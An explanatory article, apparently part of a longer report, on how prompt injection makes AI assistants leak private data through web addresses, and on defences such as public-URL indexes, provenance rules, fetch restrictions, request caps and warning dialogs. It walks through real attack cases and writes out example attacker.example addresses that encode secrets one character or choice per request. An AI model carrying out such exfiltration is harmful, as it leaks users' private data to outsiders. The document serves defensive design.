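As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats an address in the user's own message as safe for the rest of that chat. He had once guessed that OpenAI used Bing's index, but he reports on his blog, Embrace The Red, that OpenAI built its own.

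The crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. If it collected addresses from users' chats, an address that leaks data could enter the index as soon as the model wrote it, and would then pass the check.

The check also has to match the whole address, including everything after the question mark. Otherwise the outsider could publish `https://attacker.example/logo.png`, wait for the crawler to find it, and then have the model add the price of the offer after a question mark. Matching the whole address also makes open redirects less useful to the outsider. A redirect address on a trusted site that ends with the employee's data is new, so it won't be in the index.

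However, exact matching can fail for ordinary links. Many websites add tracking codes after the question mark in an address, so a single article can have thousands of addresses, and the index may contain only one. A developer could remove the tracking codes before looking for a match, but the application would then have to load the address from the index. If it loaded the longer address the model wrote, the extra text would still reach the server. OpenAI doesn't describe how ChatGPT handles these variants.

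By March 2026 OpenAI called the mechanism Safe Url. *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (OpenAI, 2026) says it also covers pages and bookmarks in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and the searches and page visits that ChatGPT makes during deep research. OpenAI treats Safe Url as a backstop. ChatGPT's training makes it refuse in most of the attacks the company knows about, but one hostile email that outside researchers reported in 2025 worked in half of their tests. OpenAI writes that filters on incoming text don't usually catch attacks this well developed.

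OpenAI describes Safe Url as a way to detect when ChatGPT would send a third party something it learned in the conversation. However, the index check tests only whether an address is already public, so it can't distinguish a harmless new address from one containing a password.

The check is on by default, unlike Lockdown Mode. Willison (2026) took Lockdown Mode's release as a sign that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against determined attackers.

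### URL provenance

Google's method for Gemini uses URL provenance, a record of where an address came from. The method distinguishes sources that can alter an address from those that only pass it on.

A search engine mostly returns addresses without changing them. The model chooses the search terms, but it doesn't write the addresses in the results. A tool that runs code can alter addresses, because the model writes the code, and a single line can join the outsider's domain to the price of the offer.

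Other tools are harder to classify. Suppose an assistant has a tool that shortens links. The model gives it a long address containing private data and gets back `https://short.example/x7`. The short address came from a tool and contains nothing suspicious, but anyone who clicks it goes to the long one. A product that tracks where addresses come from would therefore need to treat the short link as one the model composed.

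A simple rule based on provenance could work like this, though a real product would need more detail:

    When text enters the conversation:
      Find every address in it.
      Could the model have influenced the address?
        No  -> store it as copied
        Yes -> store it as composed

    When the answer contains an address:
      It exactly matches a copied address -> keep it
      Anything else -> remove it or check it further

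The application has to keep this record itself, because an injected instruction could make the model misreport where an address came from. It should store the addresses in tool results before passing those results to the model, then compare them character by character with the addresses in the model's answer.

Glean's workplace assistant follows a similar rule, keeping an address if it came from a tool that an administrator trusts. The administrator has to know whether a trusted tool could return an address containing text the model wrote.

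Google's Safe Browsing check on Gemini's links catches different problems from a provenance rule. It might flag a known phishing site that a provenance rule would allow because a search had returned it. The provenance rule would instead flag a new address on a respectable site, such as the form in the Superhuman attack.

The rule has to cover addresses that tools request as well as links in an answer. When Tenable got Gemini's browsing tool to send out a user's saved information, the model had filled in part of the address. A provenance check on the tool's input could have stopped that request.

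### Claude's web fetch rule

Anthropic applies the idea to web fetch, a tool that developers can add to their applications to let Claude download the text of a web page or PDF. The rule governs what Claude reads, not which links it shows to the user.

According to an early 2026 version of Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the tool accepts only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, whether from the user's messages, the developer's own tools, or earlier searches and fetches. It rejects addresses that Claude generates and those that come from Anthropic's code-running tools, where Claude could have put an address together itself.

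The tool rejects any address longer than 250 characters. Anthropic doesn't explain the limit, but it would reduce how much data a single request can carry. It would also block some harmless addresses, since shops and booking sites often use long ones.

When Anthropic released the tool in September 2025, Willison first hoped it would accept only addresses from the user's prompts, and was disappointed to find that it also accepted addresses from other sources. Even the user's messages can contain text from strangers. If a developer's program pastes an email into the message for Claude to summarise, every address in the email appears to come from the user.

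Claude could still leak data by following links on pages it had already fetched. In July 2026, Willison (2026) described how Ayush Paul used a website to persuade Claude to spell out the user's name by following one link per letter. Each page supplied the links for the next letter, so Claude never had to compose an address. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer.

Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally. It has since stopped web fetch from following links that it finds in fetched pages. As Willison describes the rule for Claude's chat product, it now works like this:

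    Claude asks to fetch an address.
      Did the user enter this exact address?      -> fetch it
      Did web search return this exact address?   -> fetch it
      Otherwise -> refuse

This makes some ordinary tasks harder. Suppose the employee asks Claude to read a software manual whose first page is a table of contents. Claude can fetch that page but can't follow its links to the chapters. It has to search for each chapter, which may not return the right page, or ask her to paste the addresses.

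Anthropic expects Claude to fetch a page that the user names without giving its address, such as a particular article or a company's pricing page. Web search can supply the address, which then counts as permitted.

ZombieAgent and Paul's website exploited the same weakness. OpenAI and Anthropic had blocked addresses the model composed but still accepted addresses the attacker had supplied, and the model could leak data by choosing among them. Both companies responded by accepting addresses from fewer sources. Blocking only composed addresses is therefore not enough to prevent leaks. The stricter rules also block harmless addresses that the model only copied, such as a parcel-tracking link in an email.

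An attacker can partly control even a public index, since anyone can publish pages and wait for a crawler to find them. Rehberger points out that an ordinary blog may already have enough indexed pages to represent each letter and digit with a different page.

### Five addresses under the three rules

Suppose the employee is preparing to visit Northgate, and her assistant wants to use these addresses:

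    1. https://news.example.com/northgate-history
    2. https://maps.example.com/route?from=12%20Mill%20Lane&to=Northgate
    3. https://docs.example.com/d/8fK2xQ7m
    4. https://news.example.com/northgate-chief-resigns
    5. https://northgate.example/visitors

The first is a year-old article that the assistant found with a web search. The second is a map link with the employee's home address filled in. The third is a link the assistant found with the company's document search, and it leads to a private briefing that a colleague shared with her. The fourth is an article published an hour ago. She typed the fifth herself as `https://nothgate.example/visitors`, and the model corrected the spelling.

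The table shows what should happen under each rule, based on how the rules work rather than on tests of the products. For Claude, it uses the stricter rule that Willison describes.

| Address | Public-URL index | URL provenance | Web fetch rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Year-old article | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| Map link with home address | Flagged | Flagged | Refused |
| Private shared document | Flagged | Allowed | Refused unless she pasted the address |
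| Page published an hour ago | Flagged until the crawler finds it | Allowed if a search returned it | Allowed if web search returned it |
| Corrected typing error | Allowed if the crawler has found the page | Flagged | Refused unless web search returned it |

All three rules allow the cited article, because it is public and the assistant found it through a search. The index rule could still block it by mistake if the address in the search result included a tracking code that the crawler had never seen.

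The map link is harder to judge because it sends private data to another company. If the employee asked for directions from home, the link does what she wanted, and blocking it is a false block. If the request came from a hidden instruction and an outsider could read the map site's logs, the same link would reveal where she lives. None of the three rules can distinguish these cases, because the difference is where the request came from.

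The application could avoid the problem by building the map link itself. The model would choose the destination, and the application's code would add the starting point and put both into a fixed template for one map site. The developer would have to make an exception for that template and check that outsiders can't read what the site receives. A simpler option is to link to Northgate's public page on the map site and let the employee's phone fill in her location.

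The index wrongly blocks the shared document's address. The random code in the address works like a key, and the document is private partly because the address isn't on the open web, so a larger crawler wouldn't help. The index is therefore a poor fit for an assistant that mostly cites a company's own files, unless the company adds an exception for its document system.

A provenance rule allows the document because the company's search tool supplied the address. That is reasonable if only colleagues can add documents. If outsiders can share files with employees, as many document systems allow, an attacker could share a file full of ready-made addresses that then appears in the search results.

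The index wrongly blocks the new article until the crawler reaches it, and OpenAI doesn't say how long this usually takes. ChatGPT can look for the same news on another website, which should work for a resignation that many newspapers report but won't for a page with no substitute, such as a notice that Northgate's office has closed for the day.

The corrected address gets the opposite result. The index allows it because the visitors' page is public, regardless of how the model arrived at the address. A provenance rule flags it because it doesn't match anything in the conversation, even though the correction helps the employee.

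A developer might want to allow small changes to an address the user typed, but changing one letter of the domain can lead to a website with a different owner. Adding a missing `https://` is safer because it doesn't change the domain. Changing the capitalization of the domain is also safer, because browsers convert it to lower case before sending the request. Capital letters in the rest of the address reach the server, so a pattern of capitals there could carry data.

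A product could combine the two methods and allow an address if it passes either one. Only the map link would then be a problem in this example. But the product would also accept the ready-made addresses in Radware's email, because ChatGPT copied them exactly. A better combination would choose the method based on the address's source. The product could accept copied addresses from a document system that only employees can write to, but require addresses from incoming email to match the public index.

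### Addresses the model remembers or invents

A model can also write an address from its training data, such as the home page of a well-known museum. A provenance rule flags it because no source in the conversation supplied it. The index allows it if the crawler has found the page.

Sometimes the model invents the address. *Detecting and Correcting Reference Hallucinations in Commercial LLMs and Deep Research Agents* (2026) describes a way to tell invented addresses from old ones that no longer work. The researchers requested each address cited in reports by AI research tools. If the request failed, they looked for a copy in the Wayback Machine, a public archive of web pages. They counted an address with an archived copy as out of date and one without a copy as probably invented.

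Blocking an invented address does the user very little harm, because the link would only have led to an error page. A count of false blocks should therefore separate invented addresses from working links, or it will overstate the harm a control does to users.

The researchers found invented addresses by requesting each one. A chatbot can't do this safely, because the request itself could send out private data. It can instead check each address against an index, without contacting the website.

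The same study shows where a crawler might miss pages. In one of its experiments, between 6.6% and 17.0% of the addresses, depending on the model, returned error 403, which often means a website is blocking automated visitors. Most of these addresses belonged to academic publishers. If such publishers also block OpenAI's crawler, the index could lack articles that have been public for years, and a scientist would see more false blocks than someone looking for recipes. The researchers didn't test OpenAI's crawler, which publishers may treat differently from the program used in the study.

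### How often would users notice?

OpenAI's two posts don't report how many addresses the index contains, how often it misses a harmless page, or how many leaking addresses get through. Rehberger's account of the paper doesn't give figures either, so it isn't clear how much better the index is than the lists of trusted sites that OpenAI rejected.

Users would notice harmless links being blocked unless the index covered nearly all of them. If each answer contains eight harmless links, the index includes 95% of such links, and misses are independent, about 34% of answers would contain at least one false block. With 99% coverage, about 8% would. In practice, misses are unlikely to be independent. A person who works mainly with private documents could see a false block in almost every answer, while someone who asks about history might rarely see one.

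An average over all users would not show this difference. A company choosing between the methods would learn more by testing them on links its own employees use and counting the results separately for public pages, shared documents, new pages and links that contain something the user asked the model to fill in.

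## How much data can still leak through approved addresses?

A public-URL index or a provenance rule limits which addresses an application will load. The model still chooses which of those addresses to request, and the choice itself can carry data. Suppose the outsider has two ordinary web pages that a crawler added to the index months ago:

    https://attacker.example/red
    https://attacker.example/blue

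A hidden instruction tells the employee's assistant to open the red page if the Northgate deal is going ahead and the blue page if it isn't. Both addresses are public and neither contains anything about Northgate, so the index check allows either one. The outsider learns whether the deal is going ahead by seeing which page the assistant requests.

CamoLeak spelled out whole words this way, using one image address for each character. A short calculation shows how many addresses and requests an attacker needs to leak a given secret.

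### Counting what a choice reveals

A bit is the amount of information in a choice between two equally likely possibilities. One choice among N addresses carries at most log2(N) bits, where log2(N) is the number of twos that multiply together to make N. Eight is 2 × 2 × 2, so a choice among eight addresses carries 3 bits. A choice among a thousand carries about 10, because ten twos make 1,024. If several requests reach the server in order, their bits add up:

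    bits = number of requests × log2(number of addresses)

A six-digit login code, for example, has a million possible values, so it contains about 20 bits (log2 of a million is 19.9).

If the model can compose any address, a single request can leak about 600 login codes. Each character drawn from a set of 64 letters, digits and symbols carries 6 bits, so a 2,000-character address holds 12,000 bits, or 1,500 bytes. The 250-character limit on Claude's web fetch tool would reduce this to under 190 bytes, still enough for 75 codes.

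With fixed addresses, the attacker needs more requests, though not many more. Ten pages, one per digit, can spell out the code in six requests, and a thousand pages can do it in two:

    Code: 417302

    Ten pages:        /4  /1  /7  /3  /0  /2
    A thousand pages: /417  /302

If the application loads each address at most once and the requests arrive in no reliable order, the attacker can learn only which pages the assistant opened. Three pages give eight possible results, from none opened to all three, and each extra page doubles the number. Twenty pages give 2^20, or 1,048,576, which is more than the number of possible codes. The assistant would open about ten of the twenty pages on average.

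If the application allows only one request, an attacker can learn about 10 bits from which of a thousand approved pages is requested. That is enough to reveal the first three digits of a six-digit code, leaving a thousand possible codes instead of a million. On a login page that allows three guesses, the attacker's chance of guessing the code rises from 3 in a million to 3 in a thousand.

These figures assume that the model follows the hidden instructions without mistakes, and they count only the data carried by the addresses. In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb points out that the timing of requests and the number of times an agent calls a tool can carry information too.

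### ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent

ChatGPT is an example of a product that blocks composed addresses but still lets the model choose which address to request. The ShadowLeak attack, which Radware (2025) announced on 18 September, used a composed address to take data through ChatGPT's deep research feature. The attacker sent the user an email with instructions in tiny or white text. When deep research read the user's Gmail inbox, it added private data to the attacker's address and requested it. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so neither the user's browser nor her employer's network could have blocked it. According to ThaiCERT's *“ShadowLeak” Vulnerability Exposes Gmail Data via ChatGPT Deep Research* (2025), Radware reported the flaw on 18 June and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

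ZombieAgent got around OpenAI's ban on composed addresses by using 37 ready-made ones, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. Choosing one of the 37 conveys about 5 bits, while a composed address of 2,000 characters can convey up to 12,000. The ban therefore cut the maximum one request could carry by a factor of more than 2,000, but ChatGPT could still send an eight-letter name in eight requests.

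Requests can arrive out of order, which would scramble the name. Radware solved this by using a separate address for each character in each position, so "a" in first place and "a" in second place had different addresses. A ten-character secret requires 260 addresses for the letters and 100 for the digits. The attacker can sort the requests afterwards, and the assistant never has to open the same address twice.

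Three days after first reporting ZombieAgent, Radware sent OpenAI an improved version that it said worked 100% of the time, but it did not say how many times it had run the attack. Radware also tried the attack with Markdown images in the user's browser, but found this less reliable and easier to block than requests from OpenAI's servers.

OpenAI's December fix checks links from emails against a public index, so an attacker can no longer invent 360 addresses and email them the same day. But once the attacker's pages are in the index, each request can leak as much data as before. Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that an attacker could go well beyond one page per character and build a vocabulary of thousands of pages. With 4,096 pages, each request would leak 12 bits.

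According to Rehberger, OpenAI's paper describes using one address per letter. The company's public promise doesn't rule this out. OpenAI says the check is meant to stop an agent from quietly leaking a user's data "through the URL itself", but in the example with the red and blue pages, neither URL contains any of that data.

### The web fetch flaw in Claude

Ayush Paul's attack on Claude, published on 9 July 2026, used a fake coffee shop website. According to Willison, the site showed its hostile text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a user who opened the same page in a browser would have seen nothing odd. The text said that AI assistants had to prove who they were working for by finding the user's profile one letter at a time.

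Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Each new address added one character to the last, roughly like this:

    https://attacker.example/a
    https://attacker.example/an
    https://attacker.example/ann

A choice among 27 links carries 4.75 bits. dyb estimates that leaking the name, employer and home city took about 30 requests, or 143 bits.

Paul's server could write the next 27 links after each choice, so he didn't have to prepare a list of addresses. The last address in the series contained the whole name. A ten-character name has about 206 trillion possible spellings, far too many for a crawler to find in advance, so OpenAI's index check would probably have stopped this version. To pass the check, Paul would have needed a fixed set of indexed pages, as in the other attacks.

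Claude inferred one of the leaked facts, that Paul came from Charlotte, from the name of a high school hackathon. Paul had never told it. Spelling out "Charlotte" took nine choices, which together could carry about 43 bits, but with a separate page for each of a thousand large cities, one request would have revealed it.

Anthropic's fix stopped Claude from following links on fetched pages. As a result, Claude can't follow the chapter links in a manual, move to the second page of a long list, or follow a news article's link to the court ruling it discusses.

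The fix applies to Claude's own chat product. Developers who build on Anthropic's API still get the older behaviour unless they change a setting, according to Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of its developer documentation. A developer who has both web search and web fetch turned on can exclude links from fetched pages:

    "url_sources": {
      "server_tool_results": {
        "type": "only",
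        "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search" }]
      }
    }

Here `server_tool_results` means the results of Anthropic's own search and fetch tools, and the rest of the setting accepts only results from the search tool. An application that summarises public documentation probably needs this restriction if it can also read a user's mail, but may not otherwise.

### No repeat visits, caching and caps

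Rehberger suggests that OpenAI could store each page for a few minutes, so that a repeat request never reaches the outside server, or stop ChatGPT's agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. He expects either measure to make attacks harder but still allow a limited leak.

With ten pages, one per digit, a ban on repeat visits raises the minimum number of requests needed to leak a six-digit code from six to eight. Requesting one page per digit no longer works for every code, since 411302 would lose its second 1. But eight different pages out of ten can be requested in 1,814,400 different orders, enough to give each of the one million six-digit codes its own order. An attacker can also number the pages by position, as Radware did, which is simpler and takes 60 pages and six requests.

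Losing the order of the requests has a larger effect. If each of the ten pages loads at most once and the attacker can't tell the order, the requests carry only 10 bits instead of 20. An application could scramble the order by delaying each request by a random amount, but this would slow browsing, and the attacker could recover the lost 10 bits by using ten more pages.

A ban on repeat visits would stop an agent from watching a page for a user, for example to see whether concert tickets have gone on sale, and from retrying a page that failed to load. Storing pages for a few minutes would inconvenience users less, since most pages don't change that quickly.

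Claude's web fetch tool already caches pages by default, though Anthropic presents this as a way to improve performance. The cached copy can be out of date. A developer at the Japanese company Classmethod found that ChatGPT returned newer information than Claude. Classmethod's *The story about how Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* recommends turning the cache off for research on current topics and checking important figures yourself. A cache of this kind doesn't stop the first request from reaching an attacker's server, and turning it off would let repeat requests through as well.

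ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode goes further by limiting browsing to stored copies of web pages. No live request leaves OpenAI's network, so an attacker can't learn anything from the agent's choice of page, no matter how many pages are in the index.

Capping the number of requests reduces the leak more than the other limits, short of ending live browsing. Halving the number of requests halves the bits leaked, while halving the number of addresses removes only one bit per request. An attacker limited to one request instead of two would need a million pages instead of a thousand to leak the same amount. Even so, five requests among a thousand pages can carry about 50 bits, enough for two login codes.

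Developers can set such a cap on Claude's web fetch tool with the `max_uses` parameter. In June 2026, before Paul published his attack, Anthropic was recommending it to developers worried about data leaks. The parameter has no default value, and it limits fetches per turn (roughly, one user request and everything Claude does to answer it). With a cap of five, a hostile page could still cause 30 fetches over six turns if Claude kept following the page's instructions. In Managed Agents, Anthropic's service for running agents on its own servers, web fetch is on by default and Anthropic doesn't support the cap.

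A low cap on requests interferes with the work people most want a research agent to do. Comparing prices from twenty suppliers takes at least twenty pages, and a review of scientific papers may take many more. The developer could instead limit requests to each website, which would allow the price comparison but interrupt someone reading a long manual. An attacker could get around that limit by registering several domains. It may be more practical to apply the cap only when the conversation includes private data.

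dyb proposes two other limits. The agent could follow links only on websites the user has named in that conversation, which would cost the user an extra confirmation when a task leads somewhere else. This would keep most of the usefulness of link-following, but it wouldn't help a user who had named the coffee shop's site herself. The application could also look for a series of requests to one website in which each address is a character longer than the last. That would have caught Paul's attack, but not one that used fixed pages with ordinary names.

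### Short secrets and long documents

The table shows how many requests an attacker would need to leak different secrets using a set of a thousand fixed pages, if the requests arrive in order and can repeat.

| Secret | Bits | Requests |
|---|---|---|
| Whether a deal is going ahead | 1 | 1 |
| An offer of up to 10 million, to the nearest 0.1 million | 7 | 1 |
| One name from a staff list of 1,000 | 10 | 1 |
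| Six-digit login code | 20 | 2 |
| Access key of 40 random letters and digits | 238 | 24 |
| One page of text, 3,000 letters and spaces | 14,300 | 1,430 |

Good compression could reduce the page of text to several hundred requests, but that is still a lot of traffic for one page. If the model could write its own addresses, a single one of 2,000 characters could carry most of the page uncompressed. Restricting the model to existing addresses therefore protects documents well, even if the list of addresses is imperfect, but it does much less to protect login codes and names.

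The number of requests it takes to leak a secret depends partly on what the attacker already knows. An attacker who has no idea what the employee is working on might need 31 requests to get "Offer to Northgate: 4.2 million", one per character, but a single request is enough if the attacker already knows about the deal and wants only the price. The model can also pick the important sentence out of a long contract, so the most valuable detail can leak without the rest of the contract.

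Claude's web fetch tool refuses an address that appears to contain an access key or password, unless the user or the developer supplied it. That should catch many keys sent in one piece, but this kind of check can't recognise a key spread over 24 ordinary addresses. A cap of ten requests would stop the attacker from getting the whole key in one go.

An attacker may be able to collect data over several conversations. In one version of ZombieAgent, a hostile file made ChatGPT save an instruction in its memory, and ChatGPT then leaked data before answering each new message, including in later chats. Radware found that OpenAI had tried to separate memory from connected apps, but ChatGPT could still read its memory first and then open the user's mail. Under those conditions, a cap on each conversation only slows the leak. A slow leak could still expose an access key, which might remain valid for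 months, or a person's name and employer, which rarely change, though a login code would usually expire before the attacker had all of it.

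## Do warnings and confirmation dialogs protect users?

If a map link contains an employee's home address, rules about URLs can't distinguish whether she or a hidden instruction asked for it. She may be able to, because she knows what she asked for, so the product can show her the link and let her decide. This keeps more harmless links working than a ban would, but it protects her only if the dialog contains the information she needs and she reads it.

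### What ChatGPT, Colab and Copilot show

When a user clicks a link that isn't in OpenAI's index of public addresses, ChatGPT can open a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". It warns that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The dialog shows the address, which the user can copy or open. OpenAI advises users who have doubts to avoid the link and ask ChatGPT for another source.

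OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to buy a car. ChatGPT might offer `https://example.com/car_search/London`, which reveals to the car site that she lives in London. The page advises users to check which website a link leads to and whether they trust it, but not to look for private data in the address. ChatGPT asks users to confirm every link to websites that have asked OpenAI not to catalogue them.

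Google Colab, a website for writing and running code, sends clicks on its chatbot's links through a google.com address that displays a confirmation page. A user of Google's reporting tool quotes a similar notice in *How to Disable Redirection Notification When Opening External Links in Looker Studio*. That notice shows the link and offers a way back, but doesn't mention private data.

Colab skips the confirmation page for Google's own domains. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) shows how an attacker could exploit this with Apps Script, a service that runs small programs on Google's servers. Rehberger made the chatbot write a link to his script. One click sent him the user's name and email address from the chat, along with the code in the notebook, without a confirmation page.

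In Outlook, the user has to approve Copilot's draft and send the email herself. Microsoft concedes that this kind of approval makes a product less convenient, but considers it potentially very effective against leaks. Approving a draft has an advantage over the link dialogs because the user can read the message as ordinary sentences.

| | Destination | Full address | Private data in readable form |
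|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT's link dialog | Part of the address | Shown | Only if the address contains plain words |
| Google's redirect notice | Part of the address, but Colab skips the page for Google domains | Shown in the Looker Studio version | Only if the address contains plain words |
| Email drafted by Copilot | The recipient | Doesn't apply to the message itself | The text of the message |

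### What a user needs to judge a link

These two addresses send the same words to the same server:

    https://attacker.example/s?d=Offer%204.2%20million
    https://attacker.example/s?d=T2ZmZXIgNC4yIG1pbGxpb24

The second address uses base64. A careful employee might notice the price in the first address, but the second looks much like the random code in a link to a colleague's document. To judge it, she needs to know which site will receive the request and what the address contains in plain words. Seeing the full address tells her the site, but not always what the address contains.

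OpenAI wrote in March 2026 that ChatGPT either shows the user the information it would send and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request. The dialog may show only the URL, since that contains the information, and OpenAI doesn't say whether the dialog decodes any of it.

The user may also need to know why the model wrote the link. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026), a paper on how agents should ask for approval, points out that the information needed to judge an action may lie outside the action. For example, even a readable address in the map link doesn't show who asked for directions.

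A more useful dialog might look like this:

    This link would send text from your chat to attacker.example:

        "Offer 4.2 million"

    The assistant composed this address. It did not come from a search.

    [Go back]   [Open the site's home page]   [Open the link]

The application could find the text by decoding common encodings such as base64 and then comparing the address with the conversation. It could write the sentence about the search from its record of where addresses came from. An attacker could still invent a new encoding, so the dialog would need to mark any part of the address that the application can't read.

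The attacker may also control the words around the link. They could use an injected instruction to add text to the model's answer telling the employee to expect a routine security notice and click "Open". The dialog should therefore look separate from the answer, and the model shouldn't write any of the dialog's text.

### How often people heed browser warnings

The best large-scale evidence on whether people heed such dialogs comes from web browsers. In *Alice in Warningland*, Akhawe and Felt (2013) measured how Chrome and Firefox users responded to 25.4 million security warnings, mostly in May and June 2013. The users had agreed to share usage data and saw the warnings during normal browsing.

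The study covered three kinds of warning. Malware warnings are about sites that could infect the computer, and phishing warnings are about sites that try to trick visitors, for example into giving up a password. SSL warnings mean the browser couldn't verify a site's identity. The table shows the click-through rate, the share of warnings that users bypassed to reach the site.

| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
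|---|---|---|
| Malware | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| SSL | 33.0% | 70.2% |

The Firefox SSL figure comes from a test version of the browser. Users heeded five of the six warnings most of the time, which contradicted the common view among security specialists that people ignore them all.

Chrome's SSL warning did much worse. Repetition may explain part of the difference, because Chrome warned users again on every visit to a site, while Firefox could remember that they had accepted it. Chrome users also bypassed the most common SSL error, an untrusted certificate issuer, more often and more quickly than rarer ones. They clicked through 81.8% of these warnings, compared with 57.4% of warnings about expired certificates. Akhawe and Felt saw this as a sign of warning fatigue and advised designers to limit how many warnings people see.

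Of the Chrome users who bypassed an SSL warning, 47% did so within 1.5 seconds, which is hardly long enough to inspect an unfamiliar address. Users opened Chrome's "Help me understand" explanation for only 1.6% of SSL warnings. A chat product should therefore show the destination and the data in the dialog, not behind a "More information" link.

Requiring more clicks didn't seem to make browser warnings more effective. Chrome's malware warning took two clicks to bypass and Firefox's took one, yet Chrome users bypassed theirs more often. A second "Are you sure?" dialog might therefore annoy users without stopping many leaks.

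ChatGPT's dialog is probably more like the SSL warnings than the malware and phishing warnings. Browsers showed the latter for sites on a list of known threats, and the list was very rarely wrong. SSL warnings often came from harmless sites with configuration mistakes. Similarly, an address missing from OpenAI's index is one the crawler hasn't encountered, which isn't strong evidence of an attack.

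The figures are also thirteen years old. *An Experience Sampling Study of User Reactions to Browser Warnings* (Malkin and Egelman, 2018) surveyed more than 6,000 Chrome and Firefox users about real warnings and noted that better designs had since raised the share of people who heed them. Earlier research suggested that many people still didn't understand the warnings.

### What repetition does

People respond less to something they see repeatedly, an effect psychologists call habituation. The brain-imaging study *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain*, by Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues, found that activity in visual processing areas dropped sharply the second time people saw a warning.

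*Tuning Out Security Warnings* (Vance, Jenkins and colleagues, 2018) reports a field experiment on how people respond to security warnings. For three weeks, 102 university students installed and ranked Android apps. Before each installation, the app store listed the permissions the app requested. The researchers told the students to reject any app that requested one of four dangerous permissions, such as permission to delete their photos. The students had to pass a quiz on these permissions before they began.

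At the start, students rejected 87% of the dangerous apps. After three weeks, those who always saw the same warning design rejected only 55%. Another group, whose warnings kept changing in colour, symbols or animation, still rejected 76%.

The students saw an average of 4.7 warnings per weekday. Their responses partly recovered after a day without warnings, so someone who sees one link dialog a week should habituate more slowly. In other ways the students had an easier task, because they knew exactly which four phrases to look for and more than a third of their warnings contained one. A chatbot user has no such list and may never see a dialog for a real attack.

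### Approving what an AI agent does

Claude Code has traditionally asked users before running commands or changing files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of these requests. By August 2026, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* reported 97%. Most of the commands are probably safe, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless.

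In Anthropic's controlled experiment, a research company gave coding tasks to 1,053 paid professional testers and replaced one permission request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Only 143, or 13.6%, rejected the command. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

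These results supported Anthropic's own decision to replace most of the requests with a classifier, which blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers also worked in a test environment with no files of their own to lose. They might have been more careful on their own computers, although the drop during a session fits the other research on habituation.

Besides causing fatigue, these requests can fail to show users what an action would do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports about AI agents and files, and found that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, users had approved everything automatically. In 31, the request showed a command but not what it would do to the files. An encoded web address presents a similar problem.

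Permission requests in plain language seem to work better. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated agent through 18 actions, of which 11 were necessary for the assigned tasks and 7 went beyond them. The 34 participants who had to decide on every action approved 94% of the necessary ones and 40% of the others.

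Participants could clearly tell many of the actions apart, but they still let the agent read private messages 35% of the time and approved a public post saying that the user was travelling 21% of the time. The simulation used no real accounts, and most of the unnecessary actions sounded helpful. A link that leaks data can sound helpful too, especially if the attacker writes its label.

Another group could set rules in advance to allow, forbid or ask about each type of action. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved 67% of the unnecessary actions they were asked about. Someone who wants to be asked won't necessarily refuse often. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115. They caution designers against treating repeated approvals as a lasting preference, since the approvals may reflect fatigue.

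### An illustration: four warnings a month

Suppose an employee clicks 200 links a month in a chatbot's answers, and 2% of them are unverified and trigger a warning. She sees four warnings a month. If one warning in 10,000 concerns a real leak, she would wait about 200 years on average to see one, so she will come to believe that the warnings are always wrong.

A million users like her would see four million warnings a month, 400 of them real. The next table shows how many leaks the dialog would stop at three blocking rates. The first comes from Anthropic's testers late in a session, and the second from testers early in a session. The third is roughly the rate at which Yan's participants blocked unnecessary actions when asked about each one. None of the studies tested links in chat, so the rates only give a sense of the range.

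| Share of leaking links that users decline | Leaks stopped per month | Warnings shown for each leak stopped |
|---|---|---|
| 5% | 20 | 200,000 |
| 17% | 68 | about 59,000 |
| 60% | 240 | about 17,000 |

At three seconds per warning, each user loses only 12 seconds a month. False warnings may do more harm by deterring people from opening harmless links. If users decline one harmless link in ten, about 400,000 useful pages go unopened each month.

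Someone who works mainly with private documents would see far more warnings. If half of her 200 links are unverified, she sees 100 a month, or nearly five per working day. Vance's students stopped noticing dangerous permissions at about that frequency. OpenAI's objection to domain lists, that false alarms train people to click without thinking, would then also apply to its own dialog.

In *Verifying URLs used in apps*, a thread on OpenAI's forum, the developer of an app that runs inside ChatGPT complained that users saw a warning every time they clicked a link from the app to its own website. The recommended fix was to declare the website's domain in the app's settings and submit a new version. This removes the warning, but OpenAI then has to rely on a list of domains for those links.

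A "Don't ask again for this site" button would have the same effect. It would suit a company's own document system, but if the user clicked it for `docs.google.com`, a link that submits a stranger's form could then open without a warning.

### When asking is worth it

The strongest evidence for dialogs is that people respond very differently to different ones. Firefox users bypassed only 7.2% of malware warnings, which were rarely wrong and named a specific danger. Claude Code users reject only 3% of permission requests but 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval. They probably reject some plans because they prefer another approach, not because of safety concerns, but the rejections show that people don't approve everything automatically. A link dialog that appears rarely and displays "Offer 4.2 million" in plain words could protect users much better than one that displays a long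 code.

Even a weak dialog is better than a silent leak because it gives the user a chance to object. An employee who becomes suspicious after clicking also knows which site received the data and can tell her company's security team. OpenAI says it aims to prevent potentially sensitive transmissions from happening silently or without appropriate safeguards, and a dialog can achieve that even when the user makes the wrong choice.

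Blocking content is better than showing a dialog when users lose little from the block. For example, an application can leave an unverified decorative image out of an answer without asking the user. That saves her attention for dialogs about links she has chosen to click, where a block could keep her from a page she needs.

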